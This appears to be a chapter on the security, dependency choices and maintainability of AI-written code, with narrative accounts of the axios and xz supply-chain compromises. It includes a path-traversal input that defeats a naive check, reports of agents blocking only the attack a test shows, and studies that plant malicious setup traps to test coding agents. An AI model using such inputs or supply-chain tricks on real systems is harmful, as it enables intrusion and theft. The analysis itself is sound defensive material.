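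The system SecGent writes both kinds of test before any code exists. It starts from a public catalogue of 944 types of weakness, picks the five that seem most relevant to the task, and turns one of them into an attack. Picking the right ones is difficult because a request for a feature rarely mentions what could go wrong. Searching the catalogue with the text of the task found the relevant weakness 47.1% of the time. The rate rose to 89.1% when a model first sketched what an insecure solution might look like and the system used that sketch in the search.

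Developers should also check that a security test detects the flaw it is meant to detect. Li and colleagues wrote a secure version of each network program in which they could switch off each protection separately. They accepted an attack as a test only if the complete program blocked it and the attack succeeded once they switched off the relevant protection.

AI systems can also invent attacks for a finished program. Le and colleagues' FALCON writes small attack scripts, runs them, and examines what the program did. It discards scripts that fake a success, for example by opening the secret file themselves, and reports real successes to the coding agent so that it can repair the code. On the short tasks of CWEval, FALCON raised the share of GPT-5.4 mini's solutions that were both correct and secure from 61% to 87%. On SusVibes, the secure pass rate of the larger GPT-5.4 rose only from 20.3%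 to 25.3%, averaged across three kinds of agent software. In a large project, most flaws apparently remained after the model attacked its own code.

If an attack succeeds, the program has a flaw. If every attack fails, the program has resisted those attacks, and Le and colleagues accordingly treat such a result as "no observed violation, not proof of safety". An agent that knows the test may also block only the attack it contains. For example, it could add this check to `read_note`:

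```python
if name.startswith(".."):
    raise PermissionError
```

The test now passes, but the name `./../secret.txt` leads to the same file, because a single dot means the current folder.

Researchers at the password manager company 1Password had Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 write 6,080 repairs for six complex security flaws in software such as Linux and Chrome. Only 26.0% of the repairs closed every route to the flaw without disrupting the program, according to a Japanese news report, HeadTopics' *AI生成の“修正パッチ”、4回に3回は「欠陥あり」*. The models tended to block the route that the supplied test demonstrated and overlook neighbouring ones.

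Nobody can write a test for an attack that nobody has thought of. The 0x20 defence for DNS became important after 2008, when a researcher described a new way to forge answers. Before then, a resolver could have passed a test for every published attack and still have been vulnerable to this one. Random testing can find some unknown attacks, but only if the harm is easy to recognise. A tool can detect a crash or a read past the end of an array without any information about the cause, but it needs the access policy to detect that a moderator has read a message they weren't allowed to see.

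A rule that limits what a program can do can stop attacks that no tester has imagined. If the operating system lets the notes program open only files in the notes folder, `./../secret.txt` fails, and so does any other path that leads outside the folder. But if all users keep their notes in that folder, the restriction does not stop one user from reading another's notes, so the program still needs a policy about who may read what.

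## Choice of dependencies

A developer also has to decide whose code to include in a program. Nearly all software projects reuse packages that other people wrote. Each of these lines imports a function that compares two byte strings:

```python
from hmac import compare_digest
from textkit import same
```

`hmac` is part of Python, and `textkit` is the invented package that the second password function uses. If both functions work, a login page passes the same tests with either. But with `textkit`, the page's owners have to trust everyone who can publish a new version of `textkit` or any of its dependencies, as well as Python's developers.

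The choice also has legal and practical consequences. If `textkit` is under the GNU General Public License, a company that gives customers a program containing it must also offer them the program's source code. If the only maintainer of `textkit` loses interest, there may be nobody to fix the next flaw.

### What happens during installation

To add a package, a developer or a coding agent usually lists it in a manifest, a file such as `requirements.txt` for Python or `package.json` for JavaScript. A program called a package manager does the rest:

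- It looks up the name in a registry, usually PyPI for Python or npm for JavaScript. Anyone with an email address can publish there, and neither registry reviews first uploads, according to Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*.
- It chooses a version. The entry `textkit==2.3.1` permits only that version, while `textkit>=2` permits version 2 and anything later, which usually means the newest.
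- It repeats both steps for every package that `textkit` needs, and for every package that those need. The developer may never have heard of most of them.
- It unpacks the files and may run a script that the package's author supplied. This happens before the program or any of its tests has started, and the script has the same access to the computer as the developer.

Attackers can exploit the choice of dependencies by registering a likely misspelling of a package's name (typosquatting). They can also publish a package under a name that a company uses only internally, which a package manager may then fetch instead of the internal one (dependency confusion). In *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026), Bagmar and Saraf planted such traps in projects' setup instructions and found that coding agents were much better at noticing a bad package name than a bad package source.

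### Invented package names

AI models sometimes recommend packages that do not exist. An attacker who registers one of these names can reach anyone who follows the recommendation.

Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024), in *We Have a Package for You!*, measured how often 16 models name packages that don't exist. Some of the prompts were popular questions from the programming site Stack Overflow, and a language model wrote the others from descriptions of the most downloaded packages. The models produced 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. To find out which packages each sample needed, the researchers collected its install commands and asked the model that wrote it twice, once showing it the code and once only the original request. They then checked the names against complete lists of the packages on PyPI and npm.

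Of the 2.23 million packages that the models named, 19.7% did not exist. The rate averaged 5.2% for OpenAI's commercial models and 21.7% for open models. The researchers took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each ten more times. The same name came back every time for 43% of the prompts and never for 39%. An attacker can therefore find promising names to register by asking a model the questions that developers ask.

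Churilov used the same prompts in April 2026 with five newer models, including Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The models invented between 3.6% and 5.0% of their package references, about the same as OpenAI's models two years earlier. All five invented the same 104 names, so a single malicious package could reach users of several companies' models. Few people seem to have exploited this so far. Within about six months, somebody had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, and at least one of those packages contained malware.

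A user can also supply the false package name. *Refusing the Impossible* (2026) describes a request for help with `dotenv-vault-lite`, a nonexistent npm package. Of 17 models, 16 treated the package as real, and one of those provided an install command, a list of options and a security tip.

These models answered from memory, whereas a coding agent can first look up a package name, which catches names that nobody has registered. But as Spracklen and colleagues point out, a registered package is not necessarily safe, because an attacker may already have registered the invented name.

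### Outdated and vulnerable versions

Agents also choose outdated versions of real packages. *YUL* (Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus, 2026) tested two current agents on 60 tasks, three times each, without telling them which packages to use. Claude Code with Claude Opus 5.5 declared an outdated version in 42 of the 146 runs that used the expected package (29%). OpenCode with DeepSeek V4.1 Flash did so in 54 of 139 (39%).

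The results depended heavily on the tools available. Every run that involved GitHub Actions declared an outdated version, because both agents wrote version numbers from memory, such as version 4 of a component that had reached 7.0.1. Without these runs, the rates fall to 10% and 22%. Neither agent declared an outdated version from npm or PyPI, where they mostly used commands that look up the newest one. Some of the old versions were deliberate choices for compatibility with older software.

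An outdated version is not necessarily vulnerable. Singla, Çakar and colleagues (2026), in *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making*, examined 117,062 dependency changes in popular GitHub projects and looked for flaws that were already public at the time:

| | Agents | Humans |
|---|---|---|
| Added or updated packages with a known flaw | 2.46% | 1.64% |
| Share of these for which a safe version existed | 87% | 83% |
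| Vulnerabilities introduced | 924 | 659 |
| Vulnerabilities fixed | 826 | 1,975 |

The table is weak evidence about whether agents or humans are more careful, because the two may have been working on different tasks and the agents are now at least a year old. Endor Labs reports a far higher figure, with known vulnerabilities in 49% of the versions that AI models recommend. It counts recommendations, whereas Singla and colleagues counted changes that agents submitted to real projects.

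Sharma and colleagues' tool, YUL, checks each change to a manifest before it is written to disk. It rejects nonexistent packages and outdated versions, and specifies which version to use. With YUL, Opus ended on the newest version in 39 of the 42 runs that had started with an outdated one, and DeepSeek did so in 52 of 54. In both failures, DeepSeek treated YUL's message as untrustworthy. It sometimes concluded that a version newer than its training data could not exist and that the message must be an attack.

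### Rules that a machine can enforce

YUL enforces one short rule, which is to use the newest version. Organisations can choose from several others.

An approved list names the packages a program may use. It stops invented and misspelled names if someone examines each package before adding it, but it lets through a malicious new version of an approved package. If the list covers only the packages developers request directly, it also lets through any packages that those depend on.

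Pinning records the exact version of every package, including indirect dependencies, in a lockfile. The lockfile also contains a cryptographic hash of each package, a short code calculated from its contents, so the package manager can detect whether somebody has replaced the file. Pinning keeps out malicious versions that appear later, but it does not help if the pinned version is already malicious, and it preserves known flaws until somebody updates the lockfile. In GitHub Actions, a label such as `v4` is not a pin, because the component's owner can attach it to different code. YUL therefore tells agents to use the hash of a particular version.

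A vulnerability check compares each version with a public database of known flaws. It would have caught the 924 vulnerabilities that agents introduced in Singla and colleagues' sample, but it cannot catch anything that nobody has reported. *Long-Running NPM Malware Campaign Accumulates 40,000 Downloads* (Arghire, 2026) describes eight malicious npm packages that attackers had published since August 2023. *Malicious npm Packages Hit 40,000 Downloads as Advisory Gaps Persist* (eSecurity Planet, 2026) reports that public advisories still did not cover all of them in October 2026.

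A package manager with a minimum age rule ignores any version published in, say, the last seven days. This stops attacks that security companies or early users discover quickly. It lets through malware that stays hidden for longer and delays urgent security fixes unless somebody makes an exception for them.

A licence rule permits only certain licences, and a tool enforces it by checking the licence that each package declares. This stops developers from accidentally adding a package whose terms conflict with the company's plans. The tool doesn't detect when a package's author has copied code from elsewhere and declared the wrong licence.

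A signed build record states which source repository and automatic build process produced a package. If a rule requires this record, an attacker with a stolen password cannot simply upload a package from their own computer and has to take over the build process instead. Attackers did this in May 2026 to TanStack, a family of JavaScript packages. The Hacker News' *Mini Shai-Hulud Worm Compromises TanStack, Mistral AI, Guardrails AI & More Packages* (2026) explains that they ran their own code inside the project's release process on GitHub and obtained a temporary publishing permission there. The attack affected 84 versions of 42 packages, and the malicious versions carried valid build records. Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Abuse npm Trusted Publishing in GHAPPIER Campaign*, reports another compromised package with a valid record in September.

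An inventory, also called a software bill of materials, lists a program's components and their versions. When somebody discovers a malicious version of a component, software owners can use their inventories to quickly find out which of their programs contain it. An inventory does not prevent attacks, and it can miss code that a developer or an AI system copied into the program without noting where it came from.

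### The axios compromise

Axios is a JavaScript library for sending requests to servers, with about 100 million downloads a week. In March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of it. They left its code unchanged and added one dependency, `plain-crypto-js`. VentureBeat notes that no part of axios imports this package, so adding it would not make functional tests of axios fail. The package existed only to run an installation script, which downloaded a program that gave the attackers remote control of the computer.

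The maintainer, Jason Saayman, said the attackers first posed as the founder of a well-known company and invited him to a convincing fake workspace (The Hacker News, 2026). They then gained access to his computer and npm account. The times below come from Trend Micro.

| Time (UTC) | Event | Rules that would have helped |
|---|---|---|
| Before 31 March | Attackers deceive the maintainer and take over his account | None that users of axios can apply |
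| 30 March, 23:59 | They publish `plain-crypto-js` 4.2.1 with the malicious script | None needed yet, as axios does not use it |
| 31 March, 00:21 | They publish axios 1.14.1, which depends on it | Signed build records, pinning, minimum age |
| From 00:21 | Package managers fetch `plain-crypto-js` and run its script | Approved list that covers indirect dependencies, ban on installation scripts |
| 01:00 | Attackers publish axios 0.30.4 for users of the older series | The same as for 1.14.1 |
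| About 03:30 | npm has removed the malicious versions | Inventory, to find affected computers |

Datadog Security Labs found that the attackers bypassed the project's build process and published directly from the stolen account. A rule requiring signed build records would have blocked their release but allowed the genuine version 1.14.0, which had a signed record.

The minimum age has to apply to each version, not to the package as a whole. Eighteen hours before the attack, the attackers published a harmless version of `plain-crypto-js` to give the package a history. Automatic scanners flagged the malicious version within six minutes, a quarter of an hour before axios 1.14.1 appeared. A package manager that consulted these scanners could have refused to install the malicious version.

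Requiring the newest version would have made matters worse. Elastic Security Labs reports that the attackers had marked 1.14.1 as the latest release. For about three hours, a tool like YUL would have rejected the safe version, 1.14.0, and directed agents to install the malicious one. A tool can combine the two rules by requiring the newest version that has reached the minimum age.

A ban on installation scripts would have stopped this attack and a larger one in May. The Hacker News' *Mini Shai-Hulud Pushes Malicious AntV npm Packages via Compromised Maintainer Account* (2026) describes 639 malicious versions of 323 packages, nearly all of which appeared within 22 minutes. Their installation scripts stole passwords and used them to infect further packages. But attackers can get around such a ban by hiding malicious code in the part of a package that runs when a program uses it. The Hacker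 News' *Malicious npm Package indexed-btree Hid Its Loader in Runtime Code Before Removal* (2026) describes a case from September.

### The xz backdoor

The person who put a backdoor into xz, a compression package for Linux, got access by contributing to the project, without having to steal an account. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) begins in October 2021, when somebody calling themselves Jia Tan sent the project the first of a series of harmless improvements. In 2022, several people, probably invented, complained about slow progress and urged the maintainer, Lasse Collin, to hand over to someone else. Collin replied that xz was an unpaid hobby project and that Jia Tan might take on a bigger role. By the end of that year, Jia Tan could change the code directly, and in March 2023 published a release.

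In February 2024, Jia Tan hid compiled code in two files that looked like test data. A modified build script extracted this code and inserted it into the xz library. In *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, Freund (2024) found that the modified script was only in the release archives, which Linux distributions download, and not in the public repository. On Debian and several other systems, the remote-login server loads the xz library through another library, libsystemd. The backdoor took over a function that this server uses to check login keys, which let the attacker run commands without logging in.

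Most of the rules for choosing dependencies would have let the xz backdoor through. Any list of approved dependencies for Linux would probably have included xz. Vulnerability databases had no entry for the backdoor until it was discovered. Pinning would have kept the old version only until the next update, and Jia Tan, the maintainer who added the backdoor, was pressing distributions to update. Jia Tan was also authorized to publish releases, so a maintainer's signature would have been genuine.

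A stricter rule about builds might have stopped the xz backdoor. If distributions had built xz only from the public repository, they would not have received the modified script, and the hidden code would have stayed inactive. Arch Linux switched to this method when the backdoor became public. Jia Tan could have put the script in the repository instead, but other developers would have been more likely to notice it there.

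A minimum release age of one month would have been too short, because 34 days passed between the first malicious release and the public warning. Andres Freund found the backdoor because he was running a development version of Debian that already included the new release, and he noticed that logins used a lot of processor time. A rejected login took 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. If everyone had waited longer before installing the release, he would probably have found the backdoor later.

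A change to libsystemd could have defeated the attack without anyone suspecting Jia Tan. The login server used libsystemd only to report its status, which did not require compression. On 29 February, a developer proposed that libsystemd stop loading the xz library automatically, as part of a general effort to reduce its dependencies. The project accepted the change five days later, but distributions had not yet adopted it.

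### Backdoors that are not in the source code

The xz backdoor left traces that a careful reader of the release archive could have found. Thompson (1984), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, showed how to leave none in the source code. The attack uses a compiler:

- The attacker modifies the compiler so that it inserts a backdoor whenever it compiles the login program.
- The attacker modifies it again so that whenever it compiles its own source code, it inserts both modifications into the new compiler.
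- The attacker compiles this version, installs it, and restores the original source code.

The source code of the login program and the compiler is now clean, but the installed compiler still adds the backdoor to every login program it compiles and inserts both modifications into every new version of itself. Thompson concluded that no amount of reading source code can protect people from code they have reason to distrust. The same attack would work in other programs that process code, and even in the processor's microcode.

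David A. Wheeler later described a way to detect it with a second, unrelated compiler. Let *s* be the source code of the suspect compiler *A*, let *T* be the other compiler, and let *C*(*s*) be the program that a compiler *C* produces from *s*. *T*(*s*) and *A* may consist of different instructions, but if both compilers are honest, they behave as *s* prescribes. They should therefore turn the same input into the same output:

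*A*(*s*) = (*T*(*s*))(*s*)

If *A* contains Thompson's modifications, they appear on the left side and not on the right. The test works only if the compiler always produces the same output from the same input. It misses the attack if *T* contains the same modifications, but this is much less likely than *A* alone being compromised, since the two compilers are unrelated.

### Whether to add a package and whom to trust

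None of these rules can determine whether a program needs a package at all. In Singla and colleagues' sample, 45% of the agents' dependency changes were additions, but it is unclear from the data how many were necessary. The researchers are planning a benchmark whose tasks call for different decisions. In one task, an agent has to fix date parsing in a project that already includes a suitable library, so it should not add another. In a second, it has to verify digital signatures and should use an established cryptographic library, because homemade cryptography is likely to be unsafe. A ban on new packages could therefore give the right result in the first task but the wrong one in the second.

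An agent can write a small function such as `same` in seconds, and the owners then don't have to trust an outside maintainer. However, they also get no fixes from one and are responsible for later changes themselves.

If the program does need the package, somebody has to judge its maintainers. A reviewer can check how many there are, how quickly they have fixed earlier flaws and who can publish a release. But this evidence can mislead. Jia Tan had contributed useful work for more than two years, and Saayman was an honest maintainer whom attackers deceived. A reviewer who examined xz in 2023 would have found an unpaid volunteer and a helper about whom little was known. That might have justified caution, but many useful packages depend on one or two volunteers, and rejecting them all would be impractical. Effort is better spent where a malicious package could do the most harm, so a library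 that a login server loads deserves far more scrutiny than a date formatter in a sandbox.

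## Maintainability

Maintainability is how easily later developers, human or AI, can change software correctly when prices, laws or other programs change. A team that writes a function itself instead of importing a package also has to make these changes itself. *Echoes of AI* (Borg, Hewett and colleagues, 2025) uses the definition in ISO 25010, an international standard for software quality, which defines maintainability as how effectively and efficiently people can modify a product to improve it, correct it or adapt it to new requirements.

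Code can be expensive to maintain because changes take a lot of work or because they often go wrong. Suppose that a possible change *c* has probability *p*(*c*) of being needed, takes work *w*(*c*), and introduces an error with probability *q*(*c*), which then costs *h*(*c*). The expected cost of maintenance is

Σ *p*(*c*) · (*w*(*c*) + *q*(*c*) · *h*(*c*))

summed over all possible changes. A reviewer can estimate the work and the risk of error from the code. The probabilities depend on what the owners and users will want later, which the code does not contain.

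### Two versions of one function

A shop sends parcels to France, Germany and Italy. Either of these functions calculates the postage:

```python
def postage(country, kilos):
    if country == "FR":
        if kilos <= 2:
            return 6
        return 6 + 3 * (kilos - 2)
    if country == "DE":
        if kilos <= 2:
            return 7
        return 7 + 3 * (kilos - 2)
    if country == "IT":
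        if kilos <= 2:
            return 9
        return 9 + 3 * (kilos - 2)
```

```python
BASE = {"FR": 6, "DE": 7, "IT": 9}
INCLUDED_KILOS = 2
PER_EXTRA_KILO = 3

def postage(country, kilos):
    extra = max(0, kilos - INCLUDED_KILOS)
    return BASE[country] + PER_EXTRA_KILO * extra
```

They return the same price for every parcel to these countries, so they pass and fail the same tests of prices.

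Now the shop raises the weight included in the base price from 2 to 5 kilos. A developer has to change one number in the second version but six in the first. If they overlook the last 2 in the German part of the first version, a six-kilo parcel to Germany costs 7 + 3 × (6 − 2) = 19 instead of 10. The error may go unnoticed if the new tests cover only France.

The first version would be easier to change, however, if the shop introduced a flat price for Italy. A developer would only have to replace three lines in the Italian part, whereas the second version would need a special case. A shop that expects its prices to diverge between countries might reasonably choose the first version, even though it is longer.

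### What tools can measure

Since nobody can observe future changes, tools measure features of the present code that tend to make changes harder. Most of these measures fall into five groups, and a developer or an agent can improve every one of them without improving the code:

| Measure | What a tool counts | How to satisfy it without improving the code |
|---|---|---|
| Size | Lines per function or file | Squeeze several steps into one dense line |
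| Branching | Decision points, or how deeply they are nested | Cut a function into pieces that make sense only together |
| Duplication | Lines that repeat other lines | Alter each copy until the tool no longer recognises it |
| Coupling | Links between parts of the program | Merge two parts into one large one |
| Style rules | Violations of a list, such as missing comments | Add comments that repeat what the code does |

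The usual measure of branching is cyclomatic complexity, which for simple functions is the number of decision points plus one. It is 7 for the first version of `postage` and 1 for the second. A common rule allows at most 10. This specification is short, and a machine can check it instantly. The first version would break the rule once the shop served five countries, because its complexity would be 11. An agent could then satisfy the rule by moving each country's prices into a separate function. No function would have a complexity above 6, but the included weight would still appear in ten places.

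Some evidence suggests that such measures predict later problems. CodeScene, which sells code analysis, combines more than 25 warning signs into CodeHealth, a score from 1 to 10. Borg and colleagues, some of whom work with CodeScene, cite their own earlier research, in which files with low scores had more defects and took longer to change. CodeHealth also did better than two widely used measures, from SonarQube and Microsoft, on a collection of code that experts had rated for maintainability.

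These are correlations. A file that implements a complicated tax law may have a low score and many defects because the law is complicated. In that case, tidying the file would reduce defects less than the correlation suggests.

The measures can also get worse when a developer is trying to improve the code. *Do AI Agents Really Improve Code Readability?* (2026) examined 403 changes that AI agents had described as improving readability. The Maintainability Index, which combines several traditional measures into one score, fell in 56.1% of them, and cyclomatic complexity rose in 42.7%. Either the agents often made the code worse or the measures missed real improvements, and these figures alone are not enough to tell which.

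### Asking maintainers

Another approach is to ask the people who will maintain the code. In March 2026, the research organisation METR published a study in which four active maintainers reviewed 296 AI-written changes to the open-source Python projects scikit-learn, Sphinx and pytest. Five models wrote the changes while attempting tasks in SWE-bench Verified, a benchmark that is built from real problem reports and grades solutions by running tests. The maintainers did not know whether a person or an AI had written each change. They decided whether they would accept it into the project and, if not, gave the main reason.

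The maintainers also reviewed 47 human-written changes that the projects had already accepted. They accepted only 68% of these, which shows how much such decisions vary. METR therefore divided each model's acceptance rate by 68%, so that a model with 34% of its changes accepted would get an adjusted rate of 50%. The adjusted rate was still 24 percentage points below the automatic score on average, compared with 35 points for the unadjusted rate. METR concludes that maintainers would reject roughly half of the AI-written changes that pass the tests.

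Only some of the rejections concerned maintainability. Maintainers could reject a change for poor code quality (such as wordy code or code that ignored the project's conventions), damage to other parts of the program, or failure to solve the original problem. The last two are functional errors that the tests had missed. Code quality was the only serious fault in many more of Claude Opus 4's changes than Claude 3.7 Sonnet's, largely because fewer of Opus 4's changes failed the tests. Claude Sonnet 4.5 then improved mainly on code quality.

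The study probably overstates the problem for today's agents. Its newest model is Claude Sonnet 4.5, from September 2025, and the agents had one attempt each, whereas a human contributor can usually revise a change after criticism. METR thinks that better instructions could solve many of the quality problems. But METR also told the maintainers to ignore missing tests, which made the review more lenient. The changes were small, with about 17 lines in the average human version, so the study provides little evidence about the design of a whole program.

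### Turning a maintainer's judgment into a rubric

Maintainers cannot review every change that a new model produces. The company Cognition, which sells the coding agent Devin, has tried to record their judgment once and apply it automatically. Lu, Pan and colleagues (2026), in *Introducing FrontierCode*, describe how more than 20 open-source maintainers each spent over 40 hours per task writing tasks for their own projects, together with a rubric, which is a list of criteria for a good solution. The grading uses several methods:

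- Ordinary tests check whether the program behaves correctly. Where the agent was free to choose names or error messages, a language model first adapts the tests to its choices.
- The agent's own tests run on the original, unrepaired program and have to fail there. A test that passes both before and after the repair does not show that the repair worked.
- A script checks which files the agent changed and how many lines it added.
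- A language model reads the change and scores it on questions such as whether it follows the project's conventions.

Some criteria are "blockers", meaning that the maintainer would refuse a change that didn't meet them. A solution that fails any blocker scores zero. Otherwise, its score is the weighted share of all criteria it meets.

One task, in a C++ project, was to create a function `LOG_WARNING` and use it for every warning. The function had to print to standard error, the channel for error messages. Claude Opus 4.8 consistently handled longer warnings in the second of these ways (shortened here):

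```cpp
// what the maintainer wanted
LOG_WARNING() << "This removes identifiers.\n"
              << "Few programs need this.\n";

// what the model wrote
LOG_WARNING() << "This removes identifiers.\n";
std::cerr << "Few programs need this.\n";
```

Both versions print the same text in the same place. But if a later developer makes `LOG_WARNING` write to a file, the second version will send half of each long warning to the file and the other half to the screen. The maintainer made this a blocker. It is an example of a maintainability fault that can be stated precisely, although someone had to foresee the change first.

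To test a rubric, its author tries to get a good score with a deliberately bad solution, then writes a valid solution that differs from the expected one to check that the rubric accepts it. The author also writes four solutions of varying quality and checks that the better ones score higher. These checks should catch many mistakes, but the rubric still reflects one project's preferences, and a language model applies part of it.

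Cognition's *FrontierCode 2.0* (2026) introduced a new set of tasks in October, with more projects and stricter criteria. Many of the criteria concern thoroughness. If the request mentions a fault in one part of the program, for example, the agent should also repair the same fault in a similar part. In the first version of `postage`, an agent asked to correct the French prices would have to check the German and Italian ones. These are the scores on version 2.0, including those that Journal du Net's *Fable 5.2 & Mythos 5.2* reported in November:

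| Model | Score |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 49.1% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 45.5% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 42.8% |
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 41.1% |
| Grok 4.7 | 28.6% |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 26.3% |
| Muse Wonder 1.0 | 24.3% |
| SWE-2 | 23.9% |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 19.3% |
| Kimi K3 | 17.7% |

A score of 49.1% means that at least 49.1% of the solutions would be acceptable to maintainers. The share may be considerably higher, because an acceptable solution can lose points for minor faults. The score also combines maintainability with correctness, security and speed, so a low score may have little to do with readability. Cognition has an interest in the results, but its own model, SWE-2, ranks eighth of these ten. Cognition has said that it does not plan to publish the tasks, in case models learn them in training, which makes the rubrics hard for outsiders to check.

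### Measuring later changes

The most direct way to measure maintainability is to have someone change the code and record what happens. Borg and colleagues did this with 151 participants, nearly all professional developers. In the first phase, participants added a feature to a web application for finding recipes, about half of them with AI assistants. In the second, 75 new developers each received one of the resulting programs at random and extended it without AI.

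The second group of developers took a median of 136 minutes with AI-assisted code and 173 minutes with code written without AI. This difference could easily be due to chance, since the 95% confidence interval runs from 90 minutes faster to 38 minutes slower. The average CodeHealth scores afterwards were almost the same, 8.49 and 8.44. The experiment therefore gives no sign that AI assistance made the code harder to maintain, but with 75 developers it had only about a 57% chance of detecting a medium-sized difference and a 17% chance of detecting a small one. Many participants also took breaks and had to estimate their own working times.

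The experiment took place in late 2024, when AI assistants mostly completed lines or answered questions while a developer decided what to keep. Even then, some participants let the AI write nearly everything. The two who added the most code, 10,788 and 3,094 lines, also had the two highest CodeHealth scores in the first phase. About 90% of the 10,788 lines were comments, tests and an outside library. CodeHealth is an average over files, so being much longer than necessary does not lower a program's score.

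Agents now often build on code that other agents wrote, and small faults may accumulate over many changes. *SlopCodeBench* (Orlanski, Roy et al., 2026) tests this with 36 programming problems, each divided into three to eight steps. An agent writes a program for the first step and then has to extend its own code at each later step, without knowing beforehand what that step will require. One problem starts with a tool that searches Python files. The second step adds two more programming languages and the fifth adds another three, so an agent that has written Python-specific rules into every function has a lot to rewrite.

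Orlanski and colleagues measured two kinds of decline. Verbosity is the share of lines that duplicate other lines or match one of 137 wasteful patterns. Erosion is the share of a program's complexity that sits in functions with a cyclomatic complexity above 10:

erosion = Σ_{CC(*f*) > 10} *m*(*f*) / Σ_{all *f*} *m*(*f*), where *m*(*f*) = CC(*f*) · √lines(*f*)

CC(*f*) is the cyclomatic complexity of the function *f*. Erosion rose during 77% of the runs and verbosity during 75.5%. In one run, Claude Opus 4.7 extended a program's main function from 38 lines to 240 by adding two nearly identical branches for each of seven options instead of writing one helper function.

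| | Erosion | Verbosity |
|---|---|---|
| Agents' programs | 0.68 | 0.44 |
| 473 human-run Python projects | 0.34 | 0.19 |

The comparison is somewhat unfair to the agents, because they wrote new programs under instructions that did not mention quality. When Orlanski and colleagues gave GPT-5.5 a list of bad habits to avoid, its average erosion fell from 0.49 to 0.21 and its verbosity from 0.32 to 0.21, which made its code less eroded than that of the average human project. But the share of steps at which its program passed every test also fell, from 14.8% to 9.2%. That drop may be overstated, because the 14.8% comes from the model's best run without the list. For most models, such advice improved the first version of a program but did not stop the code from getting worse afterwards.

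The average cost of a step more than doubled between the start and the end of a problem, even though the agents were changing a smaller share of the code. Some of this increase would have occurred even with perfectly clean code, because the programs were growing and had more earlier requirements to meet. To find out how much code quality matters, a researcher has to give agents the same task in clean and messy versions of the same program.

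### Whether readability still matters

*Does Code Cleanliness Affect Coding Agents?* (Trivedi and Schmitt, 2026) compared clean and messy versions of six programs. Agents made three clean programs messier, for instance by duplicating code and adding code that never runs, and cleaned up three messy ones. Tests confirmed that the two versions of each program behaved alike. Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6 then attempted 33 tasks, ten times on each version.

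The agent passed the hidden tests about equally often on the clean and less clean versions of the code. On the clean versions, it used 7–8% fewer tokens (the units of text that models read and write, and that providers charge for) and returned 34% less often to files it had already edited. Trivedi and Schmitt work for SonarSource and used its analysis tool to determine which code counted as clean, but their main result, the similar pass rates, does little to promote the tool.

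This supports the view that readability is becoming less important. If an agent succeeds as often with messy code, its owners can pay slightly more per change and never clean the code up. Trivedi and Schmitt mention that a typical task in SWE-bench Verified takes about 4 million tokens, so a saving of 7–8% would be roughly 300,000 tokens. If cleaning up part of a program took 3 million tokens, it would take about ten tasks in that part to recover them.

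Weaker models seem to need clean code more. Borg, Tornhill and colleagues (2026), in *Code for Machines, Not Just Humans*, asked models to tidy up 5,000 short Python programs from programming competitions without changing what they do. All five medium-sized models broke programs with low CodeHealth scores more often than the others. The best of the five, Qwen3-Coder, broke 28% of the low-scoring programs and 19% of the rest. Claude Code, running Claude Sonnet 4.5, broke only about 5% of each kind, with no statistically significant difference, partly because it often did little more than rename variables and adjust the layout. Competition programs are short and unlike most software, so the pattern may not hold for other code.

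A more radical proposal is to discard code whenever it becomes inconvenient and have an AI rewrite it, which fits Monperrus's view that code is disposable. But a rewrite can lose anything that the specification and tests don't cover, such as the rule that made SQLite's searches fast, a constant-time comparison or a protection against an old attack. The proposal is therefore safest for small programs with thorough specifications and for code that nobody depends on.

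Agents could also clean up after themselves. They already try to, according to *Agentic Refactoring* (2025), which examined 51,412 cases where agents restructured code in Java projects. About a quarter of the agents' changes were explicitly meant to restructure code, but these changes did not consistently reduce the number of known design faults. *A Few Pages of Markdown* (2026) cites a study of open-source projects in which complexity rose by about 39% and warnings from analysis tools rose by about 18% after the projects adopted agents. Both results involve older agents, so current ones may do better.

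The stronger reason to keep code readable is that people or other AI systems still have to check it. Trivedi and Schmitt judged the agent's programs only by functional tests, which miss many security flaws. To confirm that the shop charges every country the same price per extra kilo, a reviewer has to compare three calculations in the first version of `postage` but read only one line in the second. In a large program, a reviewer might have to find hundreds of such places and could easily overlook a flaw in one of them.

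Readability matters more when somebody will need to read more of the code. A report generator that runs in a sandbox, handles no secrets and has good tests can be untidy without much harm. Login code and access policies should be as clear as possible, even if agents make all the changes.

Teams can also use the researchers' method before accepting a large change, by having an agent make several likely future changes to a copy of the program and recording how much work each one takes and how many errors result. An agent writing the code would find it harder to pass this check with cosmetic edits than to meet a complexity limit that way, especially if it did not know which changes the team would try. But the team has to choose the right changes, because the result depends on them. The second version of `postage` would do better if the trial raised the included weight, and the first would do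 better if it gave Italy a flat price.

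## Who reads what the rules do not cover

Short rules leave some questions open, such as whether a moderator should be able to read private messages, or whether a program checks everything an attacker might send. A person or an AI system can look for the answers in the code, or developers can design the program so that mistakes in most of the code do little harm.

### The cost of human reading

Haynes estimates what it would cost to review the patches that Claude Fable 5.1 wrote in Endor Labs' security tests. The run used $672 of computing. Nobody can tell which 67 of its 156 working patches are secure without checking them all. At half an hour per patch and $100 an hour, the checking costs

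156 × 0.5 × $100 = $7,800

This is a vendor's estimate, and both the half hour and the hourly rate are assumptions. Other assumptions change the total a great deal, but reading still costs more than generating the code:

| Minutes per patch | Cost per hour | Total for 156 patches | Multiple of the computing cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | $50 | $1,300 | 2 |
| 30 | $100 | $7,800 | 12 |
| 120 | $150 | $46,800 | 70 |

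Half an hour is plausible for one careful reading. AgileConnection's *The Largest Case Study of Code Reviews—Ever* summarises a 2006 analysis of 2,500 reviews by 50 developers at Cisco, carried out by the maker of their review tool. Reviewers found fewer defects per line when they read quickly or took on more than about 200 lines at once. The article recommends reading at most 300–500 lines an hour, for no more than 60–90 minutes. The human solutions to Endor Labs' tasks average 175 lines, which would take 21 to 35 minutes at that speed. A reviewer who doesn't know the surrounding code will need longer.

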